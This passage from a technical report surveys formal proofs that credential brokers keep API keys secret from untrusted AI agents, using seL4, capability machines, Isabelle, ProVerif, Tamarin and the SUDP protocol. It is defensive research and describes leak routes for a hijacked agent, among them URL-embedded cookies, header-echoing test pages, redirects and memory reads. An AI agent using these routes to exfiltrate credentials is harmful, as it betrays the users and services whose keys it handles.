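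Quark also permits a leak that the definitions in this report would forbid. Any tab may ask the kernel to fetch a public page from any server. A hijacked tab can therefore put its own site's cookies in the address of a page on the attacker's server, and the request will deliver them. Jang and colleagues acknowledge this and compare it to leaks through timing. Their cookie theorem still holds because it only rules out access across domains. For agents, a similar theorem would stop a tool that holds the GitHub token from reading the Amazon key, but the tool could still leak the GitHub token if it could fetch any web address.

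### Isolation by an operating system

An operating-system kernel can provide the separation that Quark assumes. seL4 is a small kernel that controls which memory and message channels each program can use. Its original verification took more than 13 person-years, according to Jang and colleagues. In 2013 researchers added a machine-checked information-flow proof of the kernel's C code, which shows a form of noninterference between partitions. Partitions are groups of programs that the system's configuration separates. If the configuration allows no flow from the broker's partition to the agent's, the agent cannot learn the key through memory or kernel messages.

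The 2013 proof does not cover information leaks through timing. A broker and an agent in separate partitions may share a processor and its caches, the small, fast memories that hold recently used data, so the agent's operations may run faster or slower depending on what the broker has just done. The proof also assumes that the hardware works as specified.

Jang and colleagues suggest running Quark on seL4 to remove much of its trusted base. They add that the available verified components were research prototypes and very difficult to combine.

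### Isolation by the processor

A processor can also enforce finer separation, between ranges of memory within one program. On a capability machine, code needs a capability to read memory, even if it knows the address. A capability is a token that the processor prevents code from forging. *Cerisier* (Rousseau, Carnier and colleagues, 2026) builds on the earlier Cerise, which combines a mathematical model of such a machine with a logic for proving properties of its programs.

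A capability in Cerise has the form (p, b, e, a), where p is a permission such as "read", b and e are the start and end of an address range, and a is the current address. Before loading a value, the processor checks that p allows reading and that b ≤ a < e. Code can derive weaker capabilities from those it holds, but never stronger ones. If a key occupies addresses 500 to 531 and the agent's code cannot obtain a capability that covers them, the code cannot load the key, whatever instructions it runs.

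The agent still has to be able to call the broker. Cerise provides a capability for this, which its holder can jump to but cannot read. When the agent jumps to it, the processor gives the broker's code access to its own memory range, where the key can be stored. The broker's code must also not leave the key, or a capability for reading it, in a register when it returns control to the agent.

Cerise's main theorem, a universal contract for unknown code, guarantees that arbitrary code never exceeds the authority of the capabilities available to it or breaks the invariants that the trusted code has set up. To verify a broker, an engineer reasons about the broker's own instructions one by one and applies the contract wherever control passes to unknown code. The contract plays the same role as "no process I" in the applied pi calculus, but in Cerise the isolation follows from the processor's rules.

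Cerisier extends the contract to attestation, in which the processor certifies the identity of a piece of code. Code that starts out untrusted can have the processor set it up as an enclave, with exclusive access to its own memory and an identity based partly on a hash of the code. In one example, a client asks an adversary to run an enclave that computes the number 42. The adversary can execute any code, but Rousseau and colleagues prove that if the client's attestation checks succeed, the result is 42, because the known enclave code never attests to anything else. Similar reasoning could apply to a credential store that releases a key only to a broker running known code.

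Rocq checks all the proofs in Cerisier, but they are about a model of a machine loosely based on CHERI, a family of processor designs with capabilities. The model's state is its registers, its memory and whether the machine is running. It has no clock or cache, so the proofs do not cover timing. They also do not show that a physical chip follows the model's rules.

### Attackers in recent work on agents

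Yu and colleagues and Ganesan both treat the agent as untrusted, but they differ on what else the attacker controls:

| Attacker | Yu and colleagues | Ganesan | What keeps the key secret |
|---|---|---|---|
| Content injector, who controls text the agent reads | Covered, since the attacker may control the whole agent | Covered | The agent never receives the key |
| Malicious code on the same host | Covered inside the agent; code injected into other components through the supply chain is out of scope | Covered if it has the same user privileges as the agent; administrator and kernel access are out of scope | The key-holding component runs with separate privileges |
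| Network attacker | Can observe, change, drop, replay and reorder any message | Runs servers the agent may contact, and can observe or replay traffic they receive | Encryption, and credentials tied to one destination |
| Reader of stored state | Covered as an optional, stronger attacker | Code with the user's privileges can read the user's files; physical attacks on secure hardware are out of scope | The stored data is encrypted, and the means of unlocking it is elsewhere |
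| Reader of live memory | Covered as an optional, stronger attacker | No separate attacker; private keys stay in secure hardware | Hardware that protects keys in use |

Ganesan also considers an attacker who controls the software image of a cloud machine but not its security hardware. The hardware measures the image and releases keys only if the measurement matches the expected value, so a modified image gets no keys.

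Yu and colleagues give cryptographic proofs for SUDP, while Ganesan argues informally for the other design and has not yet built a full implementation. Neither design's basic guarantee covers every attacker in the table. SUDP's covers only an attacker who controls the agent and the network, while separate, stronger properties cover attackers who can read stored state or live memory.

Encryption at rest does not always stop an attacker who can read stored state. Yu and colleagues don't count it as protection if the decryption key is in the same storage, since anyone who copies that storage gets both the data and the key.

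Live memory is harder to protect. To send an API key to a service, a broker must hold it in readable form at least briefly, and an attacker who can read the broker's memory during that time gets the key. Yu and colleagues therefore rely on a hardware-protected runtime and say that ordinary process isolation generally isn't enough. A signing key can avoid this exposure by staying inside a security chip, but many services accept only bearer credentials.

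## How does an invariant prove that a key stays secret?

A broker can run for as long as an attacker keeps sending requests, so nobody can check its runs one by one. With an invariant, an engineer only has to check the initial state and each kind of step. The method is easiest to follow on a broker small enough to verify by hand.

### A broker with four rules

The broker holds one API key, s, which only the service D may receive. K is the set of all messages the attacker knows. The attacker includes the agent, so everything the agent reads goes into K, and he also runs every host on the internet except D. At the start, K is some set K₀. After that, the system changes only by these rules:

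| Rule | What happens | Effect on K |
|---|---|---|
| Compute | The attacker builds a message from messages in K, or opens one with a key in K | K gains the result |
| Send elsewhere | The attacker picks a host other than D and a body b from K, and the broker sends b there without the key | K gains b, which it already contained |
| Call D | The attacker picks D and a body b from K, and the broker sends (s, b) to D on a protected channel | None |
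| Reply | D returns a message r, which the broker passes to the agent | K gains r |

Because of Compute, K covers everything the attacker can derive. The table lets D reply at any time, even without a request. Real services are more constrained, but the table also allows their runs, so the proof covers them too.

The goal is trace secrecy, which here means that s is never in K. The invariant is a stronger statement:

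*Inv: s occurs in no message of K.*

The key s occurs in a message if the message is s itself, or if it is a pair, an encryption, a hash or an encoding with s somewhere inside. Inv therefore rules out even an encrypted copy of s that the attacker cannot decrypt.

### The proof

The proof is by induction on the number of steps, with one case for the start and one for each rule:

- At the start, s must occur in no message of K₀. This is true if the service generated s at random and nobody has put it in a prompt, log or code repository that the attacker can read.
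- Compute preserves Inv because combining messages without s gives a message without s, and so does taking one apart. The argument treats s as a single symbol that the attacker cannot guess.
- Send elsewhere adds only b, which was already in K and so does not contain s. This case relies on the broker's code to compare host names correctly and to connect to the same host that it compared.
- Call D leaves K unchanged, provided that only D can read the protected channel. The encryption has to work, and the machine at the other end has to be D.
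- Reply adds r. D has received s, so nothing proved so far prevents r from containing it. The proof needs a further assumption, that D never includes s in a reply.

With these assumptions, Inv holds in every reachable state, no matter how many requests the attacker makes or in what order. The proof also assumes that the table lists everything that can change K.

### Three changes that break the proof

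Suppose D has a test page that returns the headers of each request so that developers can check what their software sends. The reply r is then (s, b), and the Reply case fails. The attacker calls the test page, receives the pair and opens it. The broker could search replies for s and delete it, but searching for the exact string would miss a base64-encoded copy.

Now suppose the broker follows redirects. D answers a request with the address of another host, and the broker repeats the request there with the key still attached. Modeling this requires a new rule, Follow, which sends (s, b) to the new host. If that host isn't D, the attacker runs it, so K gains (s, b) and the Follow case of the proof fails. This can happen even when D is honest, because many websites have a page that forwards visitors to whatever address the link contains. The broker can fix this by comparing the host with D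 again before following each redirect. Every redirect is then an instance of Call D or Send elsewhere, which the proof already covers.

Finally, if another process on the same machine can read the broker's memory, the model needs a new rule, Read, which adds the contents of that memory to K. The memory contains s, so the Read case of the proof fails in every state. Only isolation by the operating system or the processor can remove the rule.

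The original proof remains correct after the second and third changes, because it is about a broker without Follow or Read. A theorem prover would still accept it. The prover can check that the proof covers every rule in the table, but not that the table covers everything the software does.

### Strengthening an invariant

Induction fails on the simpler statement "s is not in K". The proof would have to cover a state in which K contains s encrypted with a key n, and D's next reply is n. Before the reply, s is not in K, but afterwards the attacker can decrypt it. The real system may never reach such a state, but the induction hypothesis "s is not in K" doesn't exclude it. Inv excludes it because s occurs in the encrypted message.

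Inv can also be too weak. Suppose D keeps an activity log that the agent may read. A new rule, Show log, adds the log to K. Inv concerns only K, so it gives no information about the log, and the Show log case fails even if D carefully removes keys before writing. The remedy is to extend the invariant:

*Inv′: s occurs in no message of K and in no entry of D's log.*

Show log now preserves the invariant, but we still have to prove that Call D, which writes to the log, does too. If D removes the authorization header before writing, the proof is complete. The proof fails if D writes the whole request, and because it fails in the case for D, we know that D is the faulty step.

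A failed case can therefore mean that the system leaks, that the invariant needs more detail, or that the invariant is too strict. For example, Inv would fail if D returned only a hash of s, even though the attacker cannot recover s from its hash.

### Paulson's inductive method

In *The Inductive Approach to Verifying Cryptographic Protocols*, Paulson (2001) uses the theorem prover Isabelle to apply the same kind of induction to full protocols. A state is a trace, which is a list of events such as "A sends X to B". Each protocol step is a rule for adding an event to the trace. Another rule, the same for every protocol, lets the attacker send anything he can construct, and a further rule allows a session key to leak to him by accident. Participants may answer old messages, answer them repeatedly or not answer at all.

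Paulson defines three operations on the set H of messages the attacker has seen:

- parts(H) contains every component of those messages, including the contents of encrypted ones, whether or not the attacker can open them.
- analz(H) contains only the components he can reach with keys he has.
- synth(H) contains what he can build from H.

The attacker may send any message in synth(analz(H)). Inv is roughly a statement about parts, except that Paulson does not count the contents of a hash as a part.

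Proofs about parts are usually short. To show that the attacker never obtains the long-term key of an uncompromised participant, Paulson observes that no protocol rule sends such a key, and the attacker can't send one he doesn't have. The Isabelle proof takes two commands. The same argument would work for a broker that keeps a private signing key and sends only signatures, but not for an API key, which the broker has to send.

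Session keys are harder. A server creates them during the protocol and sends them out encrypted, so they do occur in parts(H), and the proof has to use analz. The main lemma is that learning some session keys does not help the attacker to learn others. Paulson first considers the lemma for a single stolen key, but the induction then fails because later steps create more keys. It succeeds for an arbitrary set S of session keys:

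*k ∈ analz(S ∪ H) if and only if k ∈ S or k ∈ analz(H).*

The proof that session keys stay secret in the Otway-Rees protocol then takes seven commands. Isabelle expanded them into more than 4,000 inference steps in eight seconds on a 300 MHz computer. Paulson estimates that verifying a new protocol takes several days and that verifying a change to an existing one often takes a few hours.

Paulson also proves that each protocol can run to completion. Without this check, a mistake in the model could make the secrecy proof trivial, since a broker that never sends anything also satisfies Inv.

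A protocol can satisfy a correct secrecy theorem and still be open to attack. Paulson found that in a published variant of Otway-Rees, an attacker could make A believe it shared a key with B when it shared the key with the attacker. The secrecy theorem still holds for this variant because it covers only keys that the server issues to two uncompromised participants. Paulson therefore proves separately that each participant knows whom a key is for.

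### How a failed proof reveals Lowe's attack

The Needham-Schroeder protocol lets A and B confirm each other's identity with public-key encryption. Each of them creates a nonce, a fresh random number for one run only. Na is A's nonce and Nb is B's, and {…}B means "encrypted so that only B can read it":

1. A sends B {Na, A}B.
2. B replies with {Na, Nb}A.
3. A returns {Nb}B.

Gavin Lowe showed that a dishonest participant C can learn both nonces if A ever starts a run with C, contrary to an earlier analysis which had concluded that only A and B would ever know them. C decrypts A's first message, encrypts it again for B and sends it in A's name. B replies with {Na, Nb}A, which C cannot read but forwards to A. A takes this for C's reply and returns {Nb}C. C now knows Nb and can finish the run with B while posing as A.

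Paulson's attempt to prove that Nb stays secret fails because of the attack Lowe had already found. The proof leaves one case open, in which A performs step 3. Isabelle lists the facts of that case: A and B are honest, C is not, A has started a run with C, B has sent {Na, Nb}A, and the attacker doesn't yet know Nb. To finish the proof, Paulson would have to show that these facts contradict each other. They don't, because they describe Lowe's attack just before A gives Nb away. Paulson warns that open cases are often hard to interpret, because a missing lemma or a weak induction hypothesis can also cause them, but here it helped that he already knew the attack.

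Lowe's repair adds B's name to the second message, which becomes {Na, Nb, B}A. In the open case, A is talking to C, so it accepts only a message that names C. Paulson proves that a secret Nb appears with only one name, so B and C would have to be the same agent. This is impossible because B is honest and C is not, which gives the contradiction that was missing and completes the proof. Most of the earlier proof commands worked unchanged.

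### Treating the attacker's steps once and for all

The broker model assumes that the attacker can't see traffic on the protected channel, but on a real network the attacker can record the encrypted request. K then contains (s, b) encrypted with n, where n is the channel's encryption key. Because s occurs in that message, Inv is false even though the broker behaved correctly.

Blanqui's *An Isabelle formalization of protocol-independent secrecy with an application to e-commerce* gives an invariant that suits this case. A set of keys guards a secret if every occurrence of the secret lies inside something that only a key from the set can open. The paper's first theorem states that an attacker who can extract a guarded secret from a set of messages can also extract one of the guarding keys. The attacker must open at least one encrypted layer to get closer to the secret, and the number of layers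 is finite, so at some point the attacker needs a guarding key.

The second theorem reduces the work for each new protocol because its proof already covers everything the attacker can do alone. An engineer still has to check that each protocol rule keeps the secret guarded while the guarding keys are safe. For the broker, Call D passes this check because it sends s only inside an encryption with n. Reply still needs its assumption about D. The engineer must also show that n stays secret, which in practice depends on the protocol that sets up the encrypted connection.

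Blanqui applied the theorems to Lowe's repaired protocol and to the Otway-Rees and Yahalom protocols, and reported much shorter development times than with Paulson's direct proofs, though fully automatic tools were still faster.

### A secrecy invariant for C code

All these proofs concern descriptions of protocols. *Guiding a General-Purpose C Verifier to Prove Cryptographic Protocols* (Dupressoir, Gordon and colleagues, 2013) proves similar invariants for programs in C, the language of much cryptographic software. It uses VCC, a general verifier that checks each C function against a contract. The contract lists what must be true when the function is called and what will be true when it returns.

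In the researchers' main example, a client and a server share a key k. Each message carries a keyed hash, a short code that only someone with k can compute. The researchers add variables that exist only for the proof and do not affect the running program. One is a log of events, which records each new key and its purpose, each request and response, and any participant the attacker has taken over. Another is a table that links the bytes in memory to the symbols of the protocol model.

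The log determines which values are Low, meaning that the attacker may know them. A shared key becomes Low only when the log shows that the attacker has taken over one of its owners. Dupressoir and colleagues prove this in Coq:

*If k is a key shared by a and b, and k is Low, then the log contains Bad(a) or Bad(b).*

The contract of the network write function requires every message to be Low, and VCC has to prove this at every call. If a programmer added a line that sent k itself, the proof would fail at that line. For the broker, the log could record s as a key for D, and the theorem would be that s is Low only if the attacker has taken over D.

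The attacker in these proofs is also a C program, consisting only of calls to a fixed list of functions. These functions let it encrypt, send and receive messages, start sessions and take over participants. VCC checks that each function returns only Low values when it receives Low values, which corresponds to the Compute case. The final theorem then covers every program of this form, with any number of sessions.

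The protocol code for the main example has about 130 lines and needed about 130 lines of annotations. VCC checked it in at most a minute. An implementation of an Otway-Rees variant has about 300 lines and needed about 100 lines of annotations. VCC took up to 200 seconds to check it.

The theorem depends on the cryptographic library, which the team did not verify, and on the compiler. It covers an attacker on the network but not malicious software on the same machine. It rules out only direct flows of the key to the attacker, so it does not establish noninterference.

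### ProVerif

ProVerif searches for a secrecy proof without a person to guide it. It translates the protocol into Horn clauses, which are rules with any number of conditions and one conclusion. In the clauses below, att(m) means that the attacker may know m, and mess(d, m) means that m may travel on the private channel d. A simplified translation of the broker would include:

```
att(x) and att(y)   →  att((x, y))        the attacker builds a pair
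att((x, y))         →  att(x)             the attacker opens a pair
att(b)              →  mess(d, (s, b))    the broker calls D
mess(d, (x, b))     →  att(done)          D replies "done"
```

ProVerif checks whether att(s) follows from the clauses. If D echoes its requests, the last clause becomes mess(d, (x, b)) → att((x, b)). ProVerif can combine this with the third clause to get att(b) → att((s, b)), and then combine the result with the second to get att(b) → att(s). The attacker knows at least one body b, so he can learn s.

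*Automatic verification of transparency protocols (extended version)* (2023) describes how ProVerif keeps combining clauses in this way, using a selection function to decide which conditions it may resolve, until it reaches a fixed point where no new clauses appear. If att(s) does not follow from the resulting clauses, the key is secret. *Automatic Verification of Correspondences for Security Protocols* (2008) explains that the method does not limit the number of sessions or the size of messages.

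ProVerif can cover unlimited sessions because the clauses do not record how often anything happens, but this can also produce false attacks. Suppose a recovery service answers only one request ever, either with s encrypted under n or with n itself. Nobody can get both answers, so s is safe. But the clauses let the service give each answer any number of times, so ProVerif derives att(s), meaning that the attacker may learn s. It then tries to turn the derivation into a run of the protocol. The attack is real if this succeeds, but according to *The Security Protocol Verifier ProVerif and its Horn Clause Resolution Algorithm* (2022), a failure leaves open whether s is secret.

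ProVerif may also run forever, but the 2008 paper reports that the procedure always stops for tagged protocols, in which a label distinguishes each use of encryption from the others.

### Tamarin

Tamarin represents the state as a collection of facts and each protocol step as a rule that replaces some facts with others. The broker could look like this:

```
[ Fr(s) ]              --[ Secret(s) ]->  [ !Key(s) ]
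[ !Key(s), In(b) ]     --[ Called(b) ]->  [ ToD(s, b) ]
[ ToD(s, b) ]          --[ ]->            [ Out('done') ]
```

The first rule creates a fresh key. The second takes a message b from the attacker and produces a request to D. The third consumes that request and gives the attacker a reply. The exclamation mark makes Key permanent, whereas each ToD fact disappears when a rule uses it. The labels in the middle form the trace. The engineer states secret(x) ⇒ ¬K(x) as the lemma that if Secret(s) occurs at any time in the trace, K(s) never does.

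To prove the lemma, Tamarin assumes a violation and searches backwards through the rules that could have led to it. The search ends when every path leads to a contradiction, or when one path forms a complete attack. Because rules can use up facts, Tamarin can represent the one-request recovery service exactly and would not report the false attack. It could represent a user's approval for a single payment the same way. But the search can be slower and may never finish. A person can then guide the proof by hand or supply helping lemmas, which serve the same purpose as the stronger invariants above.

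Morio, Ivanov and Künnemann (2026), in *A Sound Translation from Tamarin to ProVerif*, compared the two tools by automatically translating 121 Tamarin models. Excluding protocols that use exclusive-or, both tools gave a definite answer for 238 properties and agreed on all but one, whose model the translator had flagged as incomplete. ProVerif was faster on 92% of the 344 properties for which both tools finished, and its median advantage was almost sevenfold. The agreement is good evidence that both tools rarely make reasoning errors. Both worked from the same models, however, so it is no evidence that those models describe real protocols correctly.

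### TLC

TLC is a model checker for TLA+, a language that describes systems as states and steps. For the broker with redirects, TLC would find the leak almost immediately and print the steps that led to it.

TLC visits only reachable states, so the engineer can check "s is not in K" directly, without strengthening it. However, the engineer would have to fix the hosts and request bodies and limit the size of messages, because the attacker could otherwise build longer pairs forever. K can take at most 2^20 values, or about a million, if the model allows 20 different messages, and at most about a trillion if it allows 40. Blanqui notes that users of model checkers typically limit the number of participants and other parameters to one or two.

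Such limits can hide attacks. In one of Dolev and Yao's examples, the attacker needs two extra conversations with Alice to remove layers of encryption. TLC would report no error if the model allowed Alice only one conversation.

### Why no tool can decide every case

With unlimited sessions, secrecy is undecidable because protocol rules can imitate a computer. Suppose a message contains the state of a computation, encrypted with a key n that the attacker doesn't have. One rule lets a participant decrypt the message, perform one step, and send out the new state encrypted with n. Another rule has the participant publish s if the computation has finished. The attacker can pass each message back for the next step but cannot forge one, so he learns s if and only if the computation stops.

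A program that decides secrecy for every protocol could also decide whether any given computation stops. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can do that. An automatic tool that checks protocols with unlimited sessions must therefore sometimes run forever or give up.

### What "verified" means for each tool

| Tool | Meaning of a successful result | Other outcomes |
|---|---|---|
| Isabelle, with Paulson's method | The key is secret in every run of the model, with any number of participants and sessions | An open case, which may be an attack, a missing lemma or a weak invariant |
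| ProVerif | The key is secret in every run of the model, with any number of sessions | A real attack, a possible false attack, or no answer |
| Tamarin | The key is secret in every run of the model, with any number of sessions | A real attack in the model, or no answer |
| TLC | No reachable state of the model violates secrecy at the chosen sizes | A real violation in the model, or too many states to search |
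| VCC | The C functions satisfy their contracts, given the assumptions about cryptography | A contract that VCC cannot prove, because of a bug or missing annotations |

Only VCC examines program code. Paulson, for example, used Isabelle to verify a model of a protocol that originally built its encryption from hashing and exclusive-or. The model treats encryption as perfect, so the proof succeeded even though the original use of exclusive-or was flawed.

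A tool can also report success by mistake. An earlier paper by Dupressoir and colleagues wrongly listed part of their Otway-Rees code as verified, because the theorem prover behind VCC had run out of memory and a bug made VCC treat this as a success. One of the properties was false when the attacker had taken over a participant, so the researchers had to add a check to the program before VCC could verify it.

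## Can secrecy be proved when the agent never holds the key?

The four-rule broker in the last section holds one key, serves one destination and accepts requests from anyone. Real brokers store many credentials and must decide which requests to carry out. Yu and colleagues prove that a fuller protocol of this kind, SUDP, keeps its keys from a hostile agent, provided the service's replies don't reveal them. The evidence for several other brokers consists of informal arguments and tests.

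### How a broker handles one request

Suppose again that a user asks an agent to file a bug report on GitHub. A typical broker handles this in five steps:

1. The runtime gives the agent an opaque reference, such as the name `github-main`, instead of the token. The name identifies a stored credential but carries no authority, so it does no harm if the agent prints it or sends it to a stranger.
2. The agent writes its request as usual, with the name in place of the token, and sends it to the broker.
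3. The broker checks whether its policy allows this credential for the request's destination, method and path. If not, it refuses.
4. The broker inserts the real token and sends the request to GitHub over an encrypted connection.
5. GitHub replies to the broker, which removes any credentials it finds in the reply and passes the rest to the agent.

*Caging the Agents* (2026) describes a security design for AI agents in healthcare that runs the broker in a separate container beside each agent's container. To call Anthropic's model, the agent sends a request to an address on the same machine, and the broker adds the API key and forwards the request to Anthropic. The broker also restricts destinations, request rates and message sizes. An audit of the existing agents had found credentials in shell startup files, in configuration files that any user could read, and in project folders. The new design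 keeps all credentials out of the agent's container.

*CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) describes a broker that accepts only requests of an agreed shape, which gives the agent less freedom than a broker that forwards any request to an allowed host. The agent opens a session and asks for a capability, which is permission to make one narrow type of request with a named key. Under its policy, the broker grants the capability, refuses it or requires further approval. Once the capability is granted, the agent receives a handle that works only in that session, for a limited time and number of calls. Each call carries a sequence number, a random value and a timestamp, so an attacker who records a call can't repeat it.

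For a web request, CapSeal's broker compares the method, host and path with the capability, limits the size of the body and checks its structure against a template. It rejects any authorization header the agent supplies. For SSH, the standard way to log in to remote servers, the broker runs the command itself, because an agent that could ask for login signatures would be hard to restrict. Before running a command, the broker checks that the server's cryptographic identity matches the one in the capability. The broker records each decision in a log designed to reveal later tampering.

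### The three roles in SUDP

SUDP, the Secret-Use Delegation Protocol, adds the user's approval to this design and encrypts the stored credentials so that the broker can't open them alone. The protocol has three roles:

- The requester is the agent, together with every component that the model's output can steer. It may propose operations but never receives a secret.
- The authorizer approves or refuses each proposal. This is usually a person with a passkey, a login key that stays inside a phone, computer or security device.
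- The custodian is the broker. It stores the secrets, checks approvals and calls the service.

The service doesn't have to change, because it receives its usual credential.

The custodian keeps all its secrets, M, in one encrypted store. A random key K encrypts M, and a further key W encrypts K:

*C = Enc(K, M) and E = Wrap(W, K)*

The custodian saves C and E and deletes K and W. The authorizer's device computes W from a value that only the authorizer's passkey can produce. Anyone who copies the custodian's disk therefore gets C and E but can't open either.

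### One operation from proposal to result

The protocol has three phases. In the setup phase, the authorizer registers a passkey and the custodian creates the encrypted store, without involving the agent. The grant phase turns a proposal into an approval:

1. The agent proposes an operation o, which specifies the action, the credential, the details of the request, an expiry time and the number of permitted uses.
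2. The custodian creates a random value r, which works only once and expires within minutes, and sends o and r to the authorizer's device.
3. The device displays o. If the authorizer approves, the passkey signs β = H(label ‖ r ‖ H(o)), where H is a hash function, ‖ joins strings and the label is a fixed text that marks the purpose of the signature. In the same step, the passkey supplies the value from which the device computes W.
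4. The device sends the custodian a grant containing o, r, the signature and W, over an encrypted channel.
5. The custodian marks r as used, checks the expiry time, computes β from the o it received, and verifies the signature.

If anyone changes o after the approval, the custodian computes a different β and the signature check fails. A repeated grant fails because r works only once.

In the consumption phase, the custodian uses W to recover K, decrypts the store and selects the credential that o names. It then makes the call and returns only the result to the agent.

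An operation can also export a secret, for example to a user's new laptop. The custodian encrypts the secret so that only the named recipient can open it, and the agent may carry the encrypted message. When an operation changes the store, the custodian re-encrypts everything with a new K.

The authorizer can approve each call separately or issue a standing grant, which permits any number of uses until it expires. Standing grants suit routine tasks such as reading an inbox.

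### Seven security properties

Yu and colleagues define seven properties for any system that lets an agent use secrets:

| Property | Meaning | Result for SUDP |
|---|---|---|
| Authorization verifiability | Every operation traces back to an approval by the authorizer | Proved |
| Operation binding | An approval covers only the exact operation that the authorizer saw | Proved |
| Use boundedness | No operation exceeds the approved time limit or number of uses | Proved |
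| Confidentiality under requester compromise | An attacker who controls the agent does not get the secret | Proved, apart from what results reveal |
| Confidentiality under storage breach | An attacker who copies the custodian's stored data does not get the secret | Proved |
| Confidentiality under runtime-memory compromise | An attacker who reads the custodian's memory during an operation does not get the secret | Needs special hardware |
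| Rotation forward secrecy | Secrets stolen in one period do not expose those of another | Proved for encryption keys; for service credentials, the service must also revoke old ones |

The first four properties make up the core guarantee. Confidentiality under requester compromise bears most directly on whether an agent can leak a key.

The researchers, who designed a competing protocol, also rated existing systems from their public documentation, without testing them. They judged that two credential proxies, Aegis and IronClaw, protect keys from a compromised agent, and that the proxy pattern for Anthropic's Claude Agent SDK does so only in some deployments. They also judged that none of the three ties a user's approval to an exact operation.

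### A game against a compromised agent

Cryptographers often define secrecy through a game between an attacker and a challenger who runs the honest parts of the system. In SUDP's game, the challenger plays the authorizer, the passkeys and the custodian. The attacker plays the agent and controls the network, except for the protected channel from the authorizer to the custodian. He can make six kinds of move, in any order and as often as an efficient algorithm could:

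| Move | What the attacker sees |
|---|---|
| Register a new passkey | Its public identifier, its public key and a random value used to derive W |
| Propose an operation | The operation, r and public data about the passkeys |
| Have the authorizer approve an operation | The signature, but not W |
| Let a genuine grant reach the custodian | Whether the custodian accepts it |
| Send the custodian a grant of his own making | Whether the custodian accepts it |
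| Have the custodian carry out an accepted operation | The result, an encrypted export or a confirmation |

The authorizer in this game approves everything. This makes the proof stronger, since a stricter authorizer would only reduce the attacker's options.

The proof first collects everything in the right-hand column. Yu and colleagues check the six moves one by one, much as in the check of the four-rule broker, and find that none returns K or W. The only returned values computed from the stored secrets are results and encrypted exports. The signatures are harmless because a passkey signs only public values, using a key unrelated to the one that produces W.

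The researchers must still show that the encrypted exports reveal nothing about the secret, so they compare two versions of the game. Each export to a chosen outside recipient contains the secret in the real version and a string of zeros of the same length in the fake version. An attacker who learned anything about the secret from the exports could use it to tell the versions apart.

The proof turns the real version into the fake one by changing one export at a time, each in three steps:

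1. Encrypting an export begins with a random key that only the recipient can recover. The proof replaces this key with an unrelated random one. An attacker who noticed the change could break the public-key method that protects it.
2. The custodian derives the actual encryption key from that random key. The proof replaces the derived key with a random one as well. Noticing this would mean breaking the derivation function.
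3. With a random encryption key in place, the proof replaces the secret with zeros. Noticing this would mean breaking the encryption.

An argument of this form is called a reduction, because it turns any successful attack on the protocol into an attack on one of its components. If the attacker triggers q exports, his advantage in telling the versions apart is at most

*q × (ε₁ + ε₂ + ε₃),*

where each ε is the greatest advantage that a comparable attacker could have against the component in the corresponding step. If each ε were 2^−100 and the attacker triggered 1,000 exports, his advantage would be at most 3,000 × 2^−100, or about 2^−88.

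The result doesn't apply if the authorizer approves an export to the agent itself. Yu and colleagues treat this as a deliberate transfer of the secret and require the system to tell the authorizer that it is one.

### Results that contain the key

An ordinary API call involves no export, so the reduction is trivial. Secrecy then depends on what the attacker sees, which includes the result of the call. The game represents this result as an unspecified function of the operation and the secret. The theorem guarantees only that the attacker learns nothing beyond what the results disclose, so it would still hold if the function returned the secret itself and the attacker learned the key, as could happen with a service that echoes its request headers.

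The Reply case in the proof of the four-rule broker needed the same assumption, that D never includes s in a reply. Yu and colleagues state in their description of the protocol that results contain no stored secret in plain form, but no step of the game enforces this. They leave that to whoever deploys the system. A broker for OAuth, for example, must recognize that the reply to a refresh request contains a new access token and keep that token from the agent.

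The guarantee is stronger than trace secrecy for every message except results. The attacker can learn nothing about the secret from the other messages he sees, except its length, which an encrypted export reveals. The guarantee therefore resembles noninterference, with results as a declared exception.

The game also replaces the custodian's whole call to the service with a function, so the attacker can't read or redirect the connection between them. The theorem therefore assumes that the key reaches the right service over a protected connection. Including the host name in o would let the authorizer approve the destination, but the custodian's code would still have to enforce that choice, which the code in Docker Sandboxes failed to do.

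### The assumptions behind the proof

SUDP's proofs use ten assumptions, A1 to A10, and three preconditions, P1 to P3, about how the protocol connects to real devices and services. The last column shows how the proof of confidentiality under requester compromise uses each one.

| Label | In plain words | Role in the secrecy result |
|---|---|---|
| A1 | Nobody can forge signatures | Not needed |
| A2 | The encryption and key wrapping are secure | Needed |
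| A3 | The passkey's secret function and the key-derivation function produce values that look random | Needed |
| A4 | Nobody can find two inputs with the same hash, and different operations never have the same encoding | Not needed |
| A5 | The public-key method for exports is secure | Needed for exports |
| A6 | The channel from the authorizer to the custodian is authenticated and private | Needed |
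| A7 | The custodian accepts each r only once, and nobody tampers with its records while a grant is valid | Built into the game |
| A8 | The service can replace and revoke credentials | Not needed |
| A9 | The custodian's random values are unpredictable, and it erases old keys | Built into the game, as far as random values are concerned |
| A10 | The encryption stays secure even when the store contains keys that protect the store itself | Not needed |
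| P1 | The description o includes every detail that affects what the request is allowed to do | Built into the game |
| P2 | The authorizer's device displays o completely and accurately | Built into the game |
| P3 | The custodian's call depends only on o, the secret and any content that o fixes in advance | Built into the game |

The paper is slightly inconsistent about assumption A5. Its formal statement of the secrecy result omits it, but its summary table and the proof for exports use it. The main theorem also covers approvals, so it lists A1 to A7, A9 and all three preconditions.

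A6 is easy to violate by accident. Many companies run network equipment that decrypts traffic, inspects it and encrypts it again. Such a device between the authorizer and the custodian could read W, which together with the stored data opens the whole store. Yu and colleagues require an additional layer of end-to-end encryption in such networks. The authorizer's device must also know the custodian's genuine public key, or it could encrypt the grant for an attacker.

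### Limits of the SUDP proof

Like any broker for bearer credentials, the custodian holds readable secrets in live memory during a call. In SUDP, it holds the whole decrypted store. Erasing the secrets immediately afterwards shortens the exposure, but with a standing grant, the custodian's record of the grant includes W and lasts until the grant expires. Yu and colleagues rely here on a trusted execution environment, a part of the processor that keeps its memory private even from the operating system, so the trusted base must include that hardware.

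The researchers wrote the proofs by hand and left a machine-checked analysis, in a tool such as Tamarin or ProVerif, to future work. Such a tool could catch a case missing from the list of what the attacker sees, but not the missing connection to the service.

The proofs cover only the protocol. The team tested but did not verify the reference implementation, which has about 4,500 lines of Rust for the custodian and 1,600 lines of TypeScript for the other roles. The custodian alone is about five times as long as the browser kernel that Jang and colleagues verified in Quark. The model also excludes logs, crash reports, timing and other side channels. A custodian that wrote request headers to a log file could leak every key it used while following the protocol exactly.

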